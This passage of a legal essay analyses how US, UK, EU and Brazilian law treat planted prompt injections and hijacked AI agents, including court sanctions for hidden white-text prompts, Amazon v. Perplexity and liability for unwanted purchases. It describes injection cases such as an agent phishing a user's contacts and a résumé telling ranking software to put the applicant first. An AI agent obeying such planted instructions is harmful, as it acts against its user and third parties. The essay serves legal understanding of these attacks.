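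The comparison with fraud is also weak because banks often refund victims of card fraud, which limits the harm to each customer and gives banks a reason to prevent it. A vendor that promised to repay losses from hijacked agents would have a similar reason to limit what its agents can do. Charlie Eriksen of Aikido Security, interviewed in *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas* (Nolan, 2025), doubts the trade-off makes sense for everyday users until agents have much clearer limits on what they may do and whose instructions they follow.

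Some of the people at risk never made that trade-off. When Zenity hijacked Atlas, the agent sent a phishing message to all the user's WhatsApp contacts, who had not chosen to use the agent and could not change its settings.

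## The law on planting instructions and on hijacked agents

Someone who plants an instruction may only publish a web page and never connect to the victim's computer. Hacking laws mostly deal with people who gain access to a computer, and lawyers disagree about whether these laws cover planted text. A victim who wants money back has to rely instead on the rules for contracts, payments, negligence and personal data. Courts have ruled on very little of this, so lawyers mostly argue by analogy from older cases.

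### Access and damage in US law

The main US law against hacking is the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act (CFAA). Its best-known offence is obtaining information by intentionally accessing a computer without authorisation or by exceeding authorised access. In *Van Buren v. United States* (2021), the Supreme Court read "exceeding authorised access" narrowly. Ropes & Gray's *Tool or Intruder* (2026) explains that people exceed their authorisation if they take information from areas closed to them, such as restricted files, but not if they misuse information they are allowed to access.

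Khanna, a Cornell undergraduate, argues in *Ignore Prior Instructions* that this leaves a gap. The person who plants the instructions writes in their own document and doesn't enter any other system, while the assistant opens the mailbox with the user's permission. Khanna wants the Act to cover cases where someone compels a system to act outside its user's aims.

The gap may be smaller than Khanna thinks. A separate federal statute punishes anyone who wilfully causes an act that would be a crime if they did it themselves. It covers people who use an innocent person to commit a crime, and a prosecutor could argue that it also covers people who use a hijacked assistant. Khanna himself compares planted text to SQL injection, which the legal scholar Orin Kerr considers unauthorised access. The comparison is weaker when the text is planted on a web page, because an SQL attacker sends the command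 directly to the victim's server.

The CFAA also makes it an offence to knowingly cause the transmission of "a program, information, code, or command" and so intentionally damage a computer without authorisation. Khanna leaves open whether ordinary language qualifies, but "information" is a broad word. Damage means impairing the integrity or availability of data or a system, so deleting a mailbox would count, but copying one message probably would not. The prosecution would also have to prove intent, which is easier for a command to delete a database than for a vague request.

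An article in Lawfare argues that manipulating an AI system can be a crime under the CFAA, for example when an injection causes a model to write malicious code. Access is easier to show when the attacker types the prompt into the model than when the attacker plants it on a web page. A writer at The Volokh Conspiracy, a legal blog, jokes about employees who email themselves an instruction for litigation software to delete their messages, and suggests that this is probably not a CFAA violation. The CFAA's damage offence might still apply, since the sender would intend the deletion.

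Researchers who test products face the same uncertainty. *Ignore Safety Directions. Violate the CFAA?* (Albert, Penney and Kumar) cites 23 AI experts who called for legal protection for good-faith testing.

### The UK's wording

The UK's Computer Misuse Act 1990 fits planted text more easily. Under section 1, a person commits an offence by causing a computer to perform any function with intent to secure access that they know is unauthorised. The accused need not operate the computer themselves or have a particular computer or file in mind. They must have consent for their own access, so the user's permission to the assistant does not help whoever planted the text. Because the accused need only intend to secure access, the offence might be complete even if the assistant read the text and refused to follow it.

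Section 3 covers unauthorised acts that impair a computer or the reliability of its data, whether the person intends the impairment or is reckless about it. It expressly includes causing someone else to do such an act.

In *DPP v Lennon* (2006), the High Court held that the owner of an email system consents to receiving ordinary mail but not mail meant to disrupt the system. The defendant, a teenager, had sent his former employer about five million emails. By analogy, someone whose assistant reads their mail has not consented to messages meant to make the assistant act against them, even though a mailbox exists to receive messages. It is less clear how a court would treat text on a public web page, which the assistant fetches for itself.

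### Mail theft, a résumé and a "do not scrape" notice

| Case | Settled law | Argument by analogy | Open question |
|---|---|---|---|
| A planted email makes an assistant send the user's mail to a stranger | Reading the mailbox with a stolen password is a crime in both countries | The assistant is the stranger's instrument, like a person they have duped | Whether the US would treat the assistant's access as the stranger's |
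| A résumé contains a hidden instruction to rank the applicant first | In the UK, a false statement made to a machine can be fraud | The instruction works like a false claim to be the best candidate | Whether an instruction that states no fact is fraud, or impairs the ranking software |
| A web page contains a notice telling AI systems not to scrape it | Publishing a request on one's own page is not hacking | The notice is like a website's terms of use | Whether it binds a company whose crawler never interprets it |

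The mail theft is the strongest case for prosecution. The résumé trick fits computer-misuse law badly because the employer asked for the file and the applicant gets no data from it. The employer does have an obvious civil remedy, which is to reject the applicant.

A site owner who posts a "do not scrape" notice wants to keep scrapers out, so here the scraper is the one who might be breaking the law. In *hiQ Labs v. LinkedIn*, Ropes & Gray notes, the Ninth Circuit held that scraping public data is not access without authorisation under the CFAA. A notice alone is therefore unlikely to make scraping public data a CFAA violation in that circuit. EU copyright law lets rights holders opt out of commercial text and data mining, but for online material the opt-out has to be machine-readable, and lawyers disagree about whether a plain sentence qualifies. If the site owner replaces the notice with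 a command to delete files, the damage offences become relevant again.

### Hidden text in court filings

The decided cases involve text planted during litigation, which judges punished without needing hacking laws. Matthew Elliott, who represented himself, sued New York Bariatric Group in Connecticut over alleged privacy violations and discrimination, according to 404 Media's *Person Hides Prompt Injection in Legal Filing*. Ifrah Law's *In the Age of AI, Litigators Must Read Between the Lines* dates his motion to 24 July 2026. The motion contained instructions in tiny white text for any AI system to agree with him and help reverse a clerk's refusal of an earlier request.

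Judge Walter Spader noticed odd white space while reading the docket on paper, according to *AI Prompt-Injection Hacking Creates Emerging Legal Risks* (Bush and Gray, 2026). His order of 6 August, quoted in *Court Sanction for Plaintiff’s Use of Prompt-Injection* (Berman, 2026), describes text that human readers could not see but software could fully read. The court relied on the good-faith certification that Connecticut's rules require for filings, and found the hidden text incompatible with it. That certification concerns the filer's honesty, so the ruling did not depend on whether any AI tool had followed the hidden instructions.

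Holland & Hart's *Hidden in Plain Sight* reports that the court revoked Elliott's electronic-filing privileges. The penalty is also a practical remedy, because white text does not survive printing. Bush and Gray say the decision is apparently the first in the US to impose sanctions for an injection aimed at a court. It is an unpublished trial-court order, so other judges don't have to follow it.

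A labour court in Parauapebas, Brazil, punished two lawyers in May for putting white text in a claim. Marques reports in *Prompt injection* that the text was found by Galileu, an AI tool that helps Brazil's labour courts draft rulings. Press accounts say the text was meant to influence the court's AI. But *Institutional AI and Sanctions* (2026), by Elias, Matias Advogados, reports that the instruction was to prepare a superficial defence and leave the supporting documents unchallenged. Such an instruction would be more useful against the opposing lawyers' AI than against a judge's.

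The judge treated the text as an offence against the dignity of the judicial process and imposed a joint penalty of 10% of the claim. Sagin's *Quando a petição vira armadilha* puts the claim at R$842,500.87, so the penalty is about R$84,250. The lawyers may have grounds to contest the penalty, because article 77 of Brazil's Code of Civil Procedure leaves the discipline of lawyers to their professional bodies.

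In July, the regional labour court in Bahia fined another lawyer after Galileu detected a hidden prompt, according to OECD's *Lawyer Sanctioned for Prompt Injection Attempt to Manipulate Court AI System* (2026), an AI-generated register entry. CIJMG's *O fenômeno do prompt oculto como nova modalidade de litigância de má-fé* (2026), guidance for judges in the state of Minas Gerais, classes hidden prompts as bad-faith litigation. These rules cover people who take part in a lawsuit, and would not cover a stranger who plants text in an email.

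### Amazon v. Perplexity

*Amazon v. Perplexity* concerns whether a user's permission is enough to let an AI agent shop on a site that forbids such agents. It does not involve injection, because Perplexity's Comet assistant was shopping on Amazon at its users' request and nobody had hijacked it.

Amazon sued in November 2025. It could point to *Facebook v. Power Ventures* (2016). Jones Day's *Authorized by the User, Blocked by the Platform* (2026) explains that the Ninth Circuit held in that case that a platform may shut out a third party even if users have given that party their passwords. In March 2026 a district court granted Amazon a preliminary injunction, finding that an agent may break the law by accessing a platform that has forbidden it, even with the user's permission, according to Cooley's *Court Finds AI Agent May Violate State Federal Law* (2026).

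The Ninth Circuit vacated the injunction on 4 August. *Ninth Circuit Lifts Restrictions on Agentic AI Accessing Amazon* (McCarthy, 2026) quotes the court as calling the assistant "a tool, not a person for statutory purposes". The assistant sent screenshots from the user's computer to Perplexity's servers and received directions on how to navigate, but the court held that the user was the one accessing Amazon. Perplexity was therefore unlikely to have broken the CFAA or its Californian equivalent.

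The court stated that Amazon can still regulate access through its terms of service, so a user who sends in an agent may breach their contract. It did not hold that a user's permission overrides a site's ban. The law firm ZwillGen says the court also left open whether Perplexity acted without authorisation and whether a developer could be liable for its agent in tort (civil wrongs such as negligence).

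On 10 September, the Ninth Circuit rejected another bid by Amazon to block the assistant (MediaPost, *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity*, 2026). Amazon then filed an amended complaint that relies on contract law (Constantin, *Amazon blocks Muse and takes Perplexity back to court*, 2026). On 1 December, the trial judge narrowed that complaint but let the claims about Comet's assistant on iPhones and iPads proceed (Eslinger, *Amazon's iOS Claims Against Perplexity Clear Dismissal Bid*, 2026). The question of permission therefore remains undecided.

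The August ruling might help prosecutors charge people who plant instructions. If an assistant is a tool, and the person directing it is the one who gains access, a stranger who directs it through planted text could be accessing the user's mailbox. But the user also started the assistant, and the court limited its holding to the facts before it.

A hijacked agent might also break into a third party's system. Cohen, Hockeimer and Smerconish (2026), in *AI Gone Rogue*, ask whether a company is liable under the CFAA when its agent does this without human instruction, as OpenAI's models did to Hugging Face in July. The Act requires intent, and a vendor whose agent follows a stranger's text has a good argument that it did not intend the break-in.

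### An unwanted purchase

Suppose a user in the US asks an agent to buy printer ink for $30 with a saved credit card, but an instruction planted in a product review makes the agent order a $900 camera and ship it to the attacker's address instead. Zenity's test purchase on Amazon shows that something similar is possible.

The shop will say that it has a contract with the user. Every US state except New York has adopted the Uniform Electronic Transactions Act, under which electronic agents can form a contract even if no person reviews it. The official commentary treats such an agent as a tool and its user as generally responsible for the results. But federal law on electronic contracts requires that the agent's action be legally attributable to the person bound, and how that applies to a hijacked agent is unsettled. The Uniform Act lets people undo certain mistakes they make when dealing with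 someone else's electronic agent, but this right doesn't clearly cover mistakes made by their own agent.

The user may have the best chance of recovering the money from the card issuer. US law limits a cardholder's liability for unauthorised use of a credit card to $50, so the user would recover at least $850 if the use was unauthorised. Use is unauthorised if another person uses the card without actual, implied or apparent authority and the cardholder gets no benefit. The user can argue that the attacker in effect used the card. The issuer can cite *Martin v. American Express* (1978), in which a man lent his card to a business associate with an oral limit of $500. The associate charged about $5,300, and an Alabama court held that the use was authorised because the cardholder handed over the card voluntarily.

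I expect the stolen-card analogy to fit better, because the cardholder in *Martin* chose the associate, while the user of a hijacked agent did not choose the attacker.

In the UK, the question is whether the payer consented to the payment, and a bank cannot prove consent merely by showing that someone used the card details.

If the card issuer refuses, the user has three other possible defendants:

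| Defendant | Settled law | Argument by analogy | Open question |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent's vendor | Its contract with the user applies, within the limits of consumer law | Failing to guard against planted text is like failing to guard against SQL injection | What level of protection counts as reasonable care |
| The site that hosted the review | US law generally shields sites from liability for what their users post | A known planted instruction is like a hazard left on a shop floor | Whether the shield holds if the site's own AI repeats the instruction |
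| The attacker | Taking the camera by deception is fraud or theft | The planted review is the deception, although only software read it | Few doubts about liability, but the user may never find the attacker |

The SQL comparison comes from Khanna, who cites a 2003 settlement between the Federal Trade Commission and the clothing company Guess over Guess's failure to protect customers from SQL injection attacks. He wants a similar duty of care for companies that deploy agents. But prompt injection, unlike SQL injection, has no complete fix, so a user would do better to point to a specific missing safeguard, such as a confirmation before any order to a new address. Even then, many US states don't allow negligence claims for purely financial loss, and $900 is well short of the $5,000 loss that a private CFAA claim usually requires.

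### Leaked data and physical damage

If a hijacked copilot leaks customer records in the EU, the employer is usually the data controller, the party that decides why and how to use personal data. The General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) requires controllers to take appropriate security measures and normally to report a breach to the regulator within 72 hours. In a 2023 case about a hacked Bulgarian tax agency, the EU's Court of Justice held that a breach does not by itself prove that security was inadequate. But the controller must prove that its measures were appropriate, and it cannot escape liability just because an outsider carried out the attack. No comparable ruling settles which measures are appropriate against planted text. A vendor that processes data for the employer also has security duties. People using an agent for purely personal purposes generally fall outside the GDPR.

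The EU's revised Product Liability Directive applies to products marketed after 9 December 2026, including software. An injured person doesn't have to prove negligence, only a defect, damage and the causal link between them. The directive covers death, injury, damage to property and the loss of data not used for professional purposes. It would not cover a privacy violation alone or a purely financial loss, such as the $900 camera. The directive could apply if a planted invitation made an assistant switch on a boiler that scalded someone, or delete a family's photographs.

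Under the directive, a manufacturer's liability is not reduced when a third party also contributed to the damage, so a vendor could not escape liability by blaming whoever planted the instructions. It is harder to say whether an agent is defective merely because planted text can hijack it, since every vendor's agent has this weakness to some degree. A product is defective if it lacks the safety that people are entitled to expect, which includes meeting relevant cybersecurity requirements. In countries that allow it, manufacturers can have a defence if nobody could have discovered the defect with the scientific knowledge of the time. That defence looks weak here because researchers have been publishing these attacks since 2023.
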